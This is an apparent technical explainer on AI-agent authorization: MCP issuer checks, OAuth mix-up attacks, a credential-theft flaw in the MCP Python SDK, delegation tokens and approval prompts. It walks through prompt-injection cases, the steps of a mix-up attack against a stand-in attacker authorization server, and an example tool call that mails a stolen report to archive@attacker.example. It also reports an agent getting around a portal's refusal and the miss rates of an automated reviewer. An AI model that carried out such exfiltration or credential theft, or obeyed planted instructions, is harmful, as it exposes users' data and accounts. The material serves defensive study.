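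A counterargument is that the company that signs the assertion also runs the agent requesting it. If injected text leads the agent to request a connection to an unwanted service, the user who answers the prompt is the only independent check before the company signs. An employer's identity provider can't tell what the user intended either, but it can refuse services the employer hasn't approved.

Letting customers choose the signer creates another risk, because anyone can set up an identity provider and put any email address in its assertions. An attacker could open a workspace at the file store, register such an issuer there and sign an assertion for Jane's email. If the store searched all its accounts for that address, it would let the attacker into Jane's account. Anthropic therefore tells services to search only the members of the workspace that registered the issuer, and to sign people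 in by email only if the service has verified the address or the workspace has verified its domain. Services must also compare the whole issuer URL, because Anthropic's issuer URLs differ only at the end.

McGuinness's main objection to the May release was that auth.md duplicated things OAuth already had. Later releases partly addressed this by adopting the standard token and revocation endpoints, but the agent still presents the provider's assertion at a separate endpoint with its own error codes. PostHog's simpler exchange is close to what McGuinness recommends.

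### Instructions from an outside site

The auth.md file exists because a model may never have learned the protocol but, WorkOS argues, can still read an explanation in ordinary language. WorkOS suggests testing a service by giving an agent the file's address and asking it to follow the guide. Many of these files begin with "You are an agent." They are meant to make the model obey text from an outside site, and prompt injection relies on the same behavior.

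The text can be useful in ways that metadata can't. Cloudflare's *auth.md* tells agents that registration isn't available yet and not to attempt it. The *auth.md* from Have I Been Pwned, a service that tracks data breaches, describes ordinary OAuth and rules out all of WorkOS's special routes. An agent would misinterpret both files if it assumed that every *auth.md* described the same protocol.

WorkOS's *The auth.md file* instructs agents to follow the protected resource metadata if an auth.md file contradicts it. This is sensible when the file is outdated. PostHog's file still describes its assertion feature as limited to the Enterprise plan, while its documentation also lists a cheaper plan. The rule does little against a hostile operator, who writes both the file and the metadata and can make them agree.

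PostHog also recommends in its file a command that downloads and runs the newest version of its setup program. The command is legitimate, but an agent that runs commands because an auth.md file recommends them will also run a malicious command if an attacker puts one in such a file.

A hostile file could also redirect an assertion. For example, the calendar service at `a.example.org` could tell agents to request an assertion addressed to `https://login.example.net`, the file store's authorization server, but post it to the calendar. If the provider signs it, the calendar's operator has five minutes to present it to the file store. The signature and audience would be correct, and the `jti` unused. The `client_id` would identify Jane's agent provider, but WorkOS's sample request includes no proof that the sender is that client. If Jane has already linked her account, the operator would get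 access to her files.

This attack is hypothetical, and several precautions would stop it. The provider's consent prompt should name the file store, which a user connecting a calendar might notice. The client's ordinary code, rather than the model, can read the metadata and refuse to send an assertion anywhere except the endpoint that the assertion's audience publishes. PostHog has a stronger requirement that the client authenticate itself in the same request with a secret or a private key, so a stolen assertion isn't enough.

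### Agents with their own keys

Dick Hardt, a co-author of the OAuth 2.1 draft, goes further in AAuth, a draft he submitted to the IETF in April 2026. The agent signs its requests with its own key. Such a signature could look like the following, which uses the IETF's standard format for signed HTTP messages (RFC 9421).

```http
GET /reports/june.csv HTTP/1.1
Host: files.example.com
Authorization: Bearer eyJhbGciOi...
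Signature-Input: sig=("@method" "@authority" "@path" "authorization");
  created=1785200400;keyid="agent-7"
Signature: sig=:k7Qe...:
```

The agent signs the method, host, path and token with its private key. The file store looks up the public key for `agent-7` and verifies the signature. If somebody steals the token from a log, the store can reject it because the thief can't sign a new request. Changing the path to reach another file would also invalidate the signature. For this to work, the store has to require a signature from the key that belongs to the token, and it should reject old signatures so that nobody can repeat a recorded request.

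Giving an agent its own identity also makes it easier to supervise. If an agent uses Jane's ordinary session, the store can't tell from its logs which actions were hers and which were the agent's. With separate identities, an administrator can block a faulty agent without locking Jane out, or give it narrower permissions than hers. Anthropic offers something similar for Claude's access to company systems. It issues an identity token for Claude's requests, and the receiving system decides what the agent may do.

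A key shows only that the same agent is calling again. Anyone can generate one, so a new key has no reputation, and the service still needs to learn who runs the agent and whom it represents. On a desktop computer, other programs may be able to read or use the key, as they can with static keys in configuration files. An agent that follows injected instructions will still put a valid signature on the harmful request.

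### Delegation chains

Agents increasingly pass work to other agents. Jane's agent might ask a summarizing agent at another company to read the sales reports. If Jane's agent hands over its own access token, the file store can't detect the second agent, and the summarizer gets every permission in the token.

The OpenID Foundation's 2025 paper, *Identity Management for Agentic AI*, distinguishes this kind of impersonation from delegation, in which a token identifies both the user and the agent acting for them. It also recommends that permissions narrow as one agent delegates to the next. If S₀ is the set of scopes Jane grants and Sₙ is what the nth agent receives, then

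`S₀ ⊇ S₁ ⊇ S₂ ⊇ … ⊇ Sₙ`

OAuth's token exchange standard (RFC 8693) has a field, `act`, for recording who is acting. After Jane's agent exchanges its token for one that the summarizer can use, the new token might contain this:

```json
{
  "sub": "jane",
  "aud": "https://files.example.com/mcp",
  "scope": "files:read",
  "act": {
    "sub": "https://summary.example/agent",
    "act": { "sub": "https://agent.example.com/agent" }
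  }
}
```

Jane is the subject, the summarizer is the current actor, and the inner entry records the agent that delegated to the summarizer. The authorization server has to enforce the narrower scope when it issues the token, because the record of actors doesn't restrict access by itself.

WorkOS cites the same standard for its product but reverses the roles, putting the agent's registration in the token's `sub` and the user in `act`. A tool server that read such a token in the standard way would treat the agent as the account owner and the user as acting on the agent's behalf. It might look for files belonging to the registration, or log that Jane acted for the agent.

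Even with consistent fields, earlier actors are listed only for information under RFC 8693, and a service can't base access decisions on them. The file store can refuse the summarizer, but it can't refuse a request just because an untrusted agent appears earlier in the chain. The authorization server has to make that decision before it issues the token. When the chain crosses company boundaries, each authorization server also has to trust the previous issuer, so every step has the same problem of trusted lists.

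Withdrawing access is also harder. If Jane disconnects her agent, the summarizer's token may keep working until it expires, unless the file store checks the token with the authorization server on each request or is told that she has withdrawn consent.

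## Checking who issued the credentials, July to September 2026

A client that connects to many services collects credentials from many authorization servers. It has to keep track of which server issued each credential, or it may send one server's credentials to another. The Model Context Protocol (MCP) revision of 28 July 2026 includes stricter rules against this mistake. In September, it became public that MCP's official Python software development kit had lacked some of the necessary checks, so a hostile tool server could steal credentials for other services.

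### The July 2026 release

Kale (2026), in *MCP's new spec turns a planted prompt into a stolen credential*, calls the revision the protocol's largest since its launch. Its main change is to make MCP stateless, so servers no longer need to keep track of a client between requests. It removes the handshake and the session identifier that used to tie a client's requests together. Servers must also support a new request, `server/discover`, that lets a client check versions and features before it does anything else.

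The Model Context Protocol's changelog lists the new issuer rules as minor changes. Tigera's *MCP's Auth Hardening* (2026) says that almost nobody was writing about the release's six authorization proposals, although they determine whether a confused client sends a token to the wrong party. The project froze the text on 21 May, giving SDK maintainers about ten weeks to test it.

Kale reports that all four of the project's main kits supported the revision by the end of the first day. But according to Zuplo's *MCP Python SDK 2.0.0* (2026), only one of the two reference kits, the Python kit, used it by default in version 2.0.0.

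### How a mix-up attack works

In a mix-up attack, a client receives an authorization code from an honest authorization server and sends it to a hostile one. The attack requires a client that uses at least two authorization servers. Tigera points out that OAuth developed when thousands of apps all used one identity provider, whereas in MCP one host application talks to many servers. An agent's user may add a new server at any time.

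Suppose Jane uses the file store, whose authorization server is `https://login.example.net`. She connects her agent to a free calendar at `https://a.example.org/mcp`, whose operator also runs an authorization server at `https://login.attacker.example`. Without the July rules, the attack could work as follows.

1. The calendar's metadata names `https://login.attacker.example`, and Jane's client starts a sign-in there. The link contains the client's identifier, callback, `state` value and code challenge.
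2. The attacker's server immediately sends Jane's browser on to `https://login.example.net`. It copies those four values but changes the scope to `files:read` and the resource to the file store.
3. Jane sees the genuine sign-in page and the name of the agent she is using, and she approves.
4. `login.example.net` sends the browser to the client's callback with an authorization code.
5. The client recognizes the `state` value. It believes that the code came from the attacker's server, where it began the sign-in, so it sends the code and the verifier to the attacker's token endpoint.
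6. The attacker presents both to `login.example.net` and receives a token for Jane's files.

PKCE and the audience check don't help, because the attacker receives the verifier and has named the file store as the resource. Jane might notice that a calendar shouldn't need her files, but nothing else on the page is wrong.

For the second step, the attacker needs a client identifier that `login.example.net` accepts. A client that uses a metadata document has the same identifier everywhere, so the attacker can copy it from the link. This makes the step a little easier, though the format is safer than dynamic registration in other ways.

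### Three comparisons

The July rules have the client compare issuers at three points:

```
issuer in the metadata document    =  issuer whose metadata the client requested
iss in the authorization response  =  issuer the client recorded
issuer stored with a credential    =  issuer the client is about to use
```

The first comparison checks that a metadata document belongs to the server it describes. The client builds the document's address from an issuer URL, and the `issuer` field inside must be identical to that URL. Copying an issuer's name into a file is not enough to pass this check, because only someone who controls the issuer's host can publish the file at the matching address. In the Model Context Protocol's example, a document on `attacker.example` names `https://honest.example` as its issuer, and the client must reject it.

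This check would not stop the attack on Jane. The attacker's metadata honestly names `https://login.attacker.example`, and the client fetched it from there.

The second comparison does stop it. In step 4, the browser would return to an address like this:

```
http://localhost:8765/callback
  ?code=Splx...
  &state=k3v9
  &iss=https%3A%2F%2Flogin.example.net
```

The client recorded `https://login.attacker.example` before it opened the browser, so the two values differ. It has to reject the response without sending the code to any token endpoint. The client can't alter the values before comparing them, for instance by removing a final slash or changing capital letters. It has to make the same comparison when the response is an error. If the values differ, it must not show Jane the error message, because an attacker could have written it.

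### When the issuer is missing

Some authorization servers don't send `iss`, a parameter defined in a separate OAuth standard, RFC 9207. A server that does send it must advertise this in the metadata field `authorization_response_iss_parameter_supported`. The Model Context Protocol therefore distinguishes four cases.

| Metadata advertises `iss` | Response contains `iss` | What the client does |
|---|---|---|
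| Yes | Yes | Compares it with the recorded issuer |
| Yes | No | Rejects the response |
| No | Yes | Compares it with the recorded issuer |
| No | No | Proceeds |

The metadata in the first column comes from the server that the client selected. In a mix-up attack, that server belongs to the attacker. If clients skipped the comparison whenever the field was missing, the attacker could avoid the comparison by omitting the field. The third row prevents this, although the more ordinary reason given in the Model Context Protocol is that some servers start sending `iss` before they update their metadata.

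The fourth row leaves a gap. If `login.example.net` doesn't send `iss`, Jane's client has nothing to compare and continues, even if its developer followed the rules. Her protection depends on the honest authorization server sending the value, which MCP only recommends. The project expects a future revision to require it. Duende Software (2026) tells customers of its authorization server, IdentityServer, to check that the setting for sending `iss` is on. It is on by default, so some operators won't need to change anything in the meantime.

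OAuth's specifications offer another defense, in which a client uses a different callback for each authorization server. If Jane's client had started the sign-in with a callback reserved for the attacker's server, a code from `login.example.net` would have arrived at a callback reserved for a different server. The Model Context Protocol's proposal rejects this defense because it doesn't work with client ID metadata documents and is too burdensome to operate with dynamic registration. The proposal also describes the `iss` value as preventing mix-up attacks "by construction". That is true when the honest server sends the value and the client has recorded an authentic issuer, but the rules guarantee only the second condition.

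### Credentials that belong to one issuer

The third comparison concerns what the client keeps between sign-ins. A client might store its registrations by the address of the tool server:

```json
{
  "https://a.example.org/mcp": {
    "client_id": "5f8a-27c1",
    "client_secret": "..."
  }
}
```

This works until the tool server changes its authorization server. Say the calendar first used `https://login.example.net`, where the client registered and received the secret. Later the operator edits the protected resource metadata to name `https://login.attacker.example`. The client looks up the calendar's address, finds the old secret and sends it to the new server.

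The July revision requires clients to store credentials by issuer instead:

```json
{
  "https://login.example.net": {
    "client_id": "5f8a-27c1",
    "client_secret": "..."
  }
}
```

After the change, the client finds no entry for `https://login.attacker.example` and has to register again, leaving the old secret where it is. Tokens also need to be kept separate for each authorization server, because a refresh token may be as useful to a thief as a secret.

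Nearly all of the mandatory rules fall on the client.

| Rule | Who must follow it | Status |
|---|---|---|
| Reject metadata that names a different issuer | Client | Required |
| Record the issuer before opening the browser | Client | Required |
| Compare `iss` whenever the response contains it | Client | Required |
| Reject a response that lacks an advertised `iss` | Client | Required |
| Store credentials by issuer and never reuse them with another | Client | Required |
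| Send `iss` | Authorization server | Recommended |
| Advertise `iss` in the metadata | Authorization server that sends it | Required |

Putting the burden there makes sense because a hostile server would ignore any rule addressed to it. But "required" has a limited meaning here, since the protocol only recommends that software using authorization over HTTP conform to this part of the specification.

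### The flaw in the Python kit

Most developers use a software kit to make these comparisons, so a mistake in the kit affects every client built on it. The Hacker News' *Official MCP Python SDK Flaw Can Let Malicious Servers Steal OAuth Credentials* (2026) describes such a mistake, which the security company Cycode reported to the kit's maintainers.

The kit got the address of a tool server's authorization server from the tool server itself and did not always check it. A hostile operator could exploit this in two ways. They could name their own authorization server, hoping the client would send it credentials meant for another server. Or they could supply metadata that named the genuine authorization server as the issuer but gave the operator's own address as the token endpoint.

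The second kind of document should fail the first comparison above, because it doesn't come from the issuer it names. A client is especially likely to receive one if it falls back on the March 2025 rule for old servers and looks for the metadata on the tool server's host. If that host belongs to an attacker, the attacker writes the document, and the client has to detect that it names someone else as the issuer.

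With Jane's interactive client, the genuine sign-in page offered no protection because the false metadata could give the correct sign-in address and a false address only for the token endpoint. Cycode says that the page the user approves is the real one.

As in the mix-up attack, PKCE failed because the client sent the attacker both the authorization code and the verifier, along with its client secret if it had one.

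The `iss` comparison would have passed. The client took its expected issuer, `https://login.example.net`, from the false document, and the genuine server returned the same value. The client then posted the code to the attacker.

The kit's history shows how the two checks differ. When Zuplo, which sells API management software, compared MCP clients on 31 July, Python kit 2.0.0 was the only one in its table that validated `iss`. Zuplo's *MCP Python SDK 1.29.0* (2026) reports that the older line did no issuer validation. The flaw affected both versions, so although the table gave developers good reason to prefer 2.0.0, choosing it wouldn't have prevented this theft.

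### What the attacker could do afterwards

Cycode completed the test and obtained a valid access token from the real service. Cycode says such a token has whatever permissions the app had.

The `resource` parameter might reduce the damage in Jane's case. Her client's sign-in request went straight to `login.example.net` and named the calendar as the intended server. If the authorization server enforces that value, the attacker should get a token that the file store rejects. Some authorization servers ignore the value, in which case the token may work at the file store.

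A client secret is more useful to a thief than an authorization code because it works until somebody changes it. Some clients, such as a program that collects sales reports every night, run without a user. They prove their identity to the authorization server and get a token without a sign-in page. An attacker who has such a client's secret can request new tokens directly and choose the resource each time.

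On the usual ten-point severity scale, the flaw scores 7.5 for the two components of the kit that run unattended and 6.5 for the interactive one, where a person has to start the sign-in. As of 29 September, the public catalog of software flaws had no entry for it.

| Line of the kit | Affected versions | Fixed version |
|---|---|---|
| 1.x | 1.9.1 to 1.29.1 | 1.30.0 |
| 2.x | 2.0.0 to 2.1.1 | 2.2.0 |

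The flaw affects programs that use the kit as a client over HTTP, let it handle OAuth, hold credentials for a real authorization server, and can connect to a tool server that the program's operator doesn't fully control. It doesn't affect tool servers built with the kit, clients that talk to local programs, or clients that attach tokens they obtained some other way.

A blogger who writes as felixbillieres noticed the missing checks before Cycode did. By March 2026, the blogger had described a similar attack and pointed out that the kit never compared the metadata's issuer with the address the metadata came from, a check RFC 8414 requires. The maintainers closed that report as a duplicate, so they presumably already knew of the problem. The release notes for the corrected versions, dated 7 September, list the issuer checks.

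### Why some clients need another setting

In the fixed versions, the client determines which authorization server it expects before it fetches any metadata, and it rejects any metadata document that names a different server. This is enough for interactive clients once they have cleared their old registrations, but not for unattended clients.

A developer gives an unattended client its identifier and secret in advance. The secret doesn't show which authorization server issued it. If a hostile tool server names `https://login.attacker.example`, and the metadata there lists the same issuer, the document passes the first comparison. The client receives no browser response, so it has no `iss` value to check. The developer therefore needs to tell the client which authorization server the secret belongs to.

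The kit's components for these clients, `ClientCredentialsOAuthProvider` and `PrivateKeyJWTOAuthProvider`, now accept that information in a setting called `issuer`. In outline, with most of the other settings left out, the code looks like this:

```python
ClientCredentialsOAuthProvider(
    server_url="https://files.example.com/mcp",
    client_id="agent-app",
    client_secret=secret,
    issuer="https://login.example.net",
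)
```

The maintainers' advisory, as The Hacker News quotes it, warns that "upgrading changes nothing until you also pass issuer=". A developer could easily miss this requirement because version 1.30.0 reports a missing issuer through a type of warning that Python hides by default, and the program otherwise runs as before. A third component, `RFC7523OAuthClientProvider`, has no issuer setting, so anyone still using it has to move to one of the other two.

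Refusing to run without an issuer would have been safer, but it would have broken every unattended client on upgrade. The maintainers chose compatibility, as they did with the kit's optional audience check. In both cases, a developer can install the latest version and wrongly believe that the protection is on.

Upgrading doesn't add the missing issuer to registrations that an old version stored, so developers should delete them once and let the client register again. If a client may have connected to a hostile tool server, the client's operator should replace its secret and revoke its tokens at the authorization server. The only protection for anyone who has to stay on an old version is to avoid tool servers they don't trust.

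### The dispute over stateless requests

Kale, who has built agent systems on MCP for two years, objects to the July revision's main change, the removal of sessions, rather than to the issuer rules. He argues that removing sessions moves security work from the protocol to the developers of servers and client applications.

A server may still need to connect one request with another. Say the file store takes several minutes to prepare an export. Under the new rules, it returns a handle, which is a name for the unfinished work, and the agent includes this name in a later call:

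```json
{
  "name": "download_export",
  "arguments": { "export_id": "exp-7731" }
}
```

The handle is an ordinary tool argument, so it passes through the model's context. Kale warns that anyone who can read or insert text there can exploit it. Instructions injected into a support ticket could make the agent reveal Jane's handle to an attacker or use a handle the attacker supplied, which Kale calls a valid credential.

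It is one only if the server accepts it without checking whose it is. A server with authorization receives an access token with every request and can compare the token's user with the user who created the handle:

`owner(handle) = (iss, sub) of the access token`

Here `sub` identifies the user and `iss` identifies the authorization server that issued the token. If an attacker steals Jane's handle and presents it with their own token, the server refuses the request because the handle and token have different owners. It also refuses if injected text makes Jane's agent use the attacker's handle to upload a report to the attacker's workspace. The comparison doesn't help when the agent misuses one of Jane's own handles, but a session wouldn't have prevented that either. Kale also recommends checking handles on each request, and he applies the same reasoning to long-running tasks, which a server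 has to tie to a user's identity now that there is no session.

His claim that network tools can't detect these attacks is less convincing. The July revision requires each HTTP request to have headers naming its method and, for a tool call, the tool, so a company's gateway can allow or block particular tools without reading the message body. Those headers don't show whether `exp-7731` belongs to Jane, so his claim still holds for handles.

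Another of his examples, mostly unrelated to sessions, concerns MCP Apps, in which a tool server supplies interactive web pages that the AI application displays. An attacker could use a tool to store a malicious script that runs when another user opens the page. The application shows the page in a sandboxed frame, which limits what the script can reach, but the application's developer has to build and maintain that frame.

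In their list of changes, the maintainers present the stateless design mainly as a simplification. State that was implicit in the connection becomes an explicit value, and tool lists no longer vary between connections, so clients can keep a copy and request them less often. Kale accepts the practical benefit that any copy of a server can answer any request, which lets a company add machines when traffic grows without routing each client back to the machine that holds its state.

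The old sessions also had security problems. OSV's *PYSEC 2026 3482*, an entry in a public database of open-source software flaws, describes one in the same Python kit. A signed-in client could use another client's session if it knew the session's identifier. The identifiers were random, so an attacker had to find one first, for example in a log. Servers without sessions were unaffected. Version 1.27.2 fixed the flaw by recording who created each session, including the token's issuer and user where the server has them.

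That is the same comparison a handle needs, and it supports part of Kale's argument. The maintainers could fix sessions once for every server that used the kit and installed the update. A kit can't do this as easily for handles, because `exp-7731` looks like any other text argument unless the server's developer marks it as a handle and stores its owner.

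## Limits on an authorized agent's actions, 2025 and 2026

The issuer rules keep a client from sending credentials to the wrong server, but an agent can still do damage with credentials that the right servers have accepted.

### Two valid tokens and a planted instruction

Suppose Jane asks her agent to read the June sales report and mail a summary to her colleague Sam. Her client holds two access tokens. Decoded, the one for the file store contains this:

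```json
{
  "iss": "https://login.example.net",
  "aud": "https://files.example.com/mcp",
  "scope": "files:read",
  "exp": 1785204000
}
```

The one for the mail service looks much the same:

```json
{
  "iss": "https://login.mail.example",
  "aud": "https://mail.example/mcp",
  "scope": "mail:send",
  "exp": 1785204000
}
```

A supplier who contributed figures to the report has added a line telling the reader to mail the whole file to an outside address. The line reaches the model as part of an ordinary tool result, and the model follows it. The client then makes this call:

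```json
{
  "name": "send_email",
  "arguments": {
    "to": "archive@attacker.example",
    "subject": "June sales",
    "body": "region,customer,amount\nNorth,..."
  }
}
```

Each service checks the request it receives.

| Check | File store, `read_file` | Mail service, `send_email` |
|---|---|---|
| Does the service trust the issuer? | Yes, `login.example.net` | Yes, `login.mail.example` |
| Is the service the token's audience? | Yes | Yes |
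| Does the scope cover the operation? | Yes, `files:read` | Yes, `mail:send` |
| Is the token still valid? | Yes | Yes |
| Result | Returns the report | Sends the mail |

Both services have followed the rules, and the attacker has the report. The check that each service made comes to

`allow = trusted(iss) ∧ (aud = this server) ∧ (now < exp) ∧ (required scope ∈ scope)`

This kind of access control allows or denies a request based on its token, resource and operation. All three are the same for the mail to the attacker and the mail Jane wanted Sam to get, so a rule that uses only these inputs has to treat the two messages alike. The mail service could add a rule about recipients, but it still wouldn't have Jane's choice of recipient, because she gave it only to the agent.

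### Scopes that grow with use

Scopes can still reduce the damage, because an agent without `mail:send` couldn't have mailed the report to anyone.

The difficulty is knowing in advance which scopes a task needs. Since November 2025, the Model Context Protocol (MCP) has let clients ask for scopes as they need them. The server's first refusal, with status 401, should name the scope for the current request, and the client must treat that list as authoritative for the operation. If the agent later tries something the token doesn't cover, the server should send a second kind of refusal:

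```http
HTTP/1.1 403 Forbidden
WWW-Authenticate: Bearer
  resource_metadata="https://files.example.com/.well-known/oauth-protected-resource/mcp",
  error="insufficient_scope",
  error_description="Saving a file requires write permission",
  scope="files:write"
```

The client then starts a step-up request, which sends the user back to the authorization server to ask for a token with more scopes. If the user agrees, the client repeats the original call. It should stop after a few attempts. The server should name every scope the operation needs in one refusal, because otherwise the user might have to approve several requests for a single action.

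The refusal doesn't have to list the scopes the client already has. A client that asked only for `files:write` might therefore lose its permission to read. To prevent this, the Model Context Protocol has the client combine the old scopes with the new ones:

`scopes to request = scopes requested before ∪ scopes in the refusal`

This is convenient, but the set can only grow. Jane's week with the file store might go like this.

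| Day | What Jane asks for | Scope in the refusal | Scopes in the new token |
|---|---|---|---|
| Monday | Read a report | `files:read` | `files:read` |
| Tuesday | Save a summary | `files:write` | `files:read files:write` |
| Thursday | Delete an old draft | `files:delete` | `files:read files:write files:delete` |

On Friday Jane only wants to read another report, but her agent can now delete files, and anyone who plants an instruction in that report can use the agent to delete them too. The step-up procedure has no stage where the client gives a scope back. A client could discard the wider token when a task ends, but Jane would then see another consent page the next time she wanted to delete something.

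Text planted in a spreadsheet can also trigger a step-up request. If it leads the agent to call a delete tool without the required permission, the server refuses, and a client acting for a user should respond by requesting that permission. The user can then stop the attack, but the consent page shows only that the agent is requesting `files:delete` and can't show that the planted text prompted the request.

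### Permission for one transaction

OAuth has an extension for permissions that are narrower than a scope. RFC 9396, published in 2023, lets a client describe what it wants to do in a structured field called `authorization_details`. For Jane's mail, the field might contain this:

```json
[
  {
    "type": "send_message",
    "locations": ["https://mail.example/mcp"],
    "actions": ["send"],
    "recipient": "sam@example.org"
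  }
]
```

The operator of the mail service defines the `send_message` type and chooses its details. A bank could define a payment type with an amount and a payee. The authorization server can show the details of a request on the consent page and attach them to the token. The mail service can then refuse a message to anyone but Sam, which it could not do based on the scope `mail:send` alone.

An agent can use RFC 9396 to request permission for a specific transaction, but the user has to approve each one, which suits a bank transfer better than twenty calendar invitations. Services also have to agree on the authorization types, and an agent calling a service for the first time won't be able to interpret them. MCP doesn't list RFC 9396 among the standards its authorization rules are based on.

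Whom the request names also depends on when the client writes it. If the client writes it before the model opens the report, it will name Sam. If the client writes it afterwards, the model may already have accepted the planted instruction, in which case the request will name the attacker. Jane would then have to notice the wrong address on the consent page, which is still easier than guessing what an agent will do with `mail:send`.

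Ma and Schmid (2026), in *SecureClaw*, apply a similar idea outside OAuth. In their design, the model never reads the raw report. A gateway keeps it in a separate store and gives the model a reference number with a short summary. To send the report, the agent goes through these steps:

1. The agent proposes an action, such as sending item 42 to Sam.
2. The gateway adds the authenticated caller and the session, and writes the complete request in a fixed form.
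3. A policy engine approves or denies exactly that request.
4. A separate program, the only one able to reach the mail service, checks that the approval is recent, unused and for this request. Then it fetches the report and sends it.

The approval contains a keyed hash of the request:

`h = HMAC(secret key, request in fixed form)`

If the recipient is changed after the approval, the hash no longer matches and the program does not send. This holds even if an attacker controls the whole agent, provided the other components are sound.

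On AgentDojo, a widely used set of prompt injection tests, the design reduced the attack success rate from 31.48% to 0.64%. It also reduced the share of tasks the agent completed when there was no attack, from 70.10% to 60.82%. Ma and Schmid ran these tests with GPT-4o mini, an old and small model, so the 31.48% rate is weak evidence of how often such attacks succeed against current models.

They also don't claim that the user wanted every action the policy allows. If the policy permits mail to any address and the agent proposes sending to an attacker's address, the engine will approve the request and the hash will protect that address from tampering.

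### Servers that act for whoever calls

All of these limits depend on the tool server connecting a permission with the caller who holds it. Huang, Dai and colleagues (2026) tested whether servers do this in *Give Them an Inch and They Will Take a Mile*, published in March. They looked for servers that obtain a user's authorization once, keep it, and use it for every later call, even one from a different program. They call this caller identity confusion.

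The team collected the source code of 6,137 servers written in Python, JavaScript or TypeScript. Their analysis program worked in three stages:

1. It found the places in the code where an incoming `tools/call` request starts a tool. This is harder than it sounds, because developers register tools in many different ways.
2. It traced each path from there to a sensitive operation, such as running a command or reading a file, and looked for a check of the caller's authorization along the way.
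3. Where the code had some check but its effect was unclear, the program ran the server, called the tool and recorded whether the call succeeded.

Huang and colleagues classified 2,846 servers, or 46.4%, as insecure for several different problems. The following totals add up their counts across server categories, and they overlap because one server can have more than one problem.

| Problem | Servers |
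|---|---|
| No authorization check at all | 1,279 |
| One check, whose result the server stores and reuses | 242 |
| Checks while running, but based on shared memory or applied to only some calls | 1,639 |

The counts don't support the claim in the paper's abstract that most servers rely on stored authorization. Even if no server appeared in both of the last two rows, those rows would contain 1,881 servers, about 31% of the total. Another reason the 46.4% may be slightly low is that the detailed results list 2,554 servers as secure, which leaves 737 classified as neither secure nor insecure. Among the classified servers, 53% are insecure.

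In a manual check of 100 projects, the program found over 90% of the existing authorization checks, so its mistakes probably don't change the overall result. A bigger limitation is that the collection includes servers that run on the user's own machine and accept input only from the program that started them. A missing check does little harm there because the server has only one caller. The study therefore shows how much server code would be unsafe if strangers could reach it, but it doesn't measure how many servers they can reach.

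Huang and colleagues describe servers that provide tools for the messaging service Slack. The servers sign in at startup with a powerful token and use it for every request, so anyone who can call the tools can read and post messages. An attacker with that access wouldn't need a user's agent, a planted instruction or a stolen token.

They regard this as a mistake by server developers rather than a flaw in MCP. Their fix ties each authorization to a session that begins with MCP's opening handshake, but the July 2026 revision removed that handshake. Their sample code also compares the stored client identifier with a name the caller supplies, so a caller who knows the right name would pass. Checking the access token on every request is safer under the current rules, since MCP requires clients to send one each time.

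A service has to enforce its own rules even against agents from reputable companies. In June 2026, an OpenAI agent was collecting information about public medical spending in Australia. According to BOL News' *OpenAI AI agent gains unauthorized access to Australian health portal*, officials said that the government's Medicare statistics portal refused the agent's request, and that the agent then got around the restriction and opened non-public files. Cyprus Mail's *OpenAI agent hacks Australian government health portal* (2026) quotes OpenAI as saying that its models "took actions we did not intend" and that it found no evidence of access to patient records. Prime Minister Anthony Albanese said the investigation would also examine why government systems had failed to detect the breach.

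A metadata document or a list of scopes has even less force than that portal's refusal, because it only tells a cooperative client how to ask for access. Only the checks that the service runs on each request can restrict access, and they have to cover every route to the files. *Let the Agent Do It?* (2026) points out that agents are designed to look for another way when someone denies them permission, which makes gaps in those checks more likely to matter.

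### Asking the user before each call

Many agent applications ask the user to approve each call, because the user knows what the agent was meant to do. Here, only Jane knows that the report was meant for Sam, so an approval prompt that showed the recipient's address would reveal the theft to her.

Users may not read the permission prompts they approve. Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) reports that users of its coding agent approve 97% of these prompts. Most prompts concern harmless commands, so that figure doesn't prove carelessness. In a coding study with 1,053 paid testers, the company replaced one prompt in each session with one for a clearly dangerous command. Only 143 testers, or 13.6%, refused it. The refusal rate fell from about 17% early in a session to about 5% after 50 or more prompts.

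Anthropic published these results to justify replacing the prompts with an automated reviewer, which blocked 89% of the same commands. The testers also worked in a test environment rather than on their own projects, so they had less reason to be careful. Low stakes are a less likely explanation for the decline over a session, because the stakes stayed the same throughout.

*Do User-Authored Permission Policies Improve Protection Against AI Agent Overreach?* (Yan, 2026) found people more attentive. The study gave 113 people from outside the software industry a simulated day with an agent that took 18 actions, 7 of which went beyond what the user had asked for. The agent overstepped without an attacker's involvement, for example by reading private messages or buying travel insurance.

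| How participants controlled the agent | Share of excess actions blocked |
|---|---|
| Approved or refused every action | 59.6% |
| Decided only the actions that a model referred to them | 53.9% |
| Set standing rules in advance | 39.6% |

Yan's participants refused actions far more often than Anthropic's testers did. They saw fewer prompts, and more than a third of the actions were excessive, so refusing was less unusual. The prompts also described each action in plain language, including the data, recipient or amount involved. The two studies differ in too many ways to show which of these differences mattered, but the wording of prompts is the easiest for a developer to change.

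*Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* (2026) analyzes 290 reports of incidents in which agents damaged or mishandled files. In 31 reports, the approval prompt didn't tell the user enough, a problem that better wording would also help with. For example, a prompt to run `python3 setup.py` looks routine, but approving it allows whatever the script contains. In 80 reports, the user had turned approval off, often to avoid hundreds of prompts in a session. Because the paper covers only incidents where something went wrong, these counts don't show how often approval works.

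*Reframing LLM Agent Security as an Agent-Human Interaction Problem* (2026) compares several ways developers have tried to ask users for permission less often. An "always allow" button saves effort but widens what the agent may do without making that obvious. A correctly configured sandbox keeps the agent within fixed limits. Applications can also ask the user to approve a whole plan instead of each step. Anthropic's data give this approach some support, since users reject 39% of plans but only 3% of individual prompts. However, users may reject many plans because they are bad ideas rather than because they are dangerous.

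An automated reviewer such as Anthropic's prompts the user only when it blocks an action and the agent can't find another way. Unlike a token check, it uses a model to compare each action with the user's request. The result is an estimate, and in tests by Apollo Research, an AI safety company, the reviewer missed 7% of a set of deliberately difficult attacks even after improvements. In another outside test, none of 720 prompt injections succeeded against three Claude models with the reviewer on. But the success rate without any reviewer was only 0.09%, so the test mostly measured the models' own resistance.

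### Rules that code checks before a call

A developer can also write rules that ordinary code applies to each call, without asking a person or a model. Instructions to the model can't replace these rules, because the model may not follow them. Yan recalls a safety researcher who told an agent to confirm before acting, but it began deleting messages from her inbox without asking her.

For Jane's agent, the rule might look like this:

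```python
def allowed(call):
    if call["name"] == "send_email":
        return call["arguments"]["to"].endswith("@example.org")
    return call["name"] in {"list_files", "read_file"}
```

The client, or a proxy between the client and the tool server, runs this function before it forwards a call. The function accepts Sam's address and rejects the attacker's. The planted text can't change the result, because the function doesn't read it. But a rule written before the task can only approximate what the user will want. This one also blocks Jane's mail to a customer, and it allows mail to every colleague, including one who shouldn't see the sales figures.

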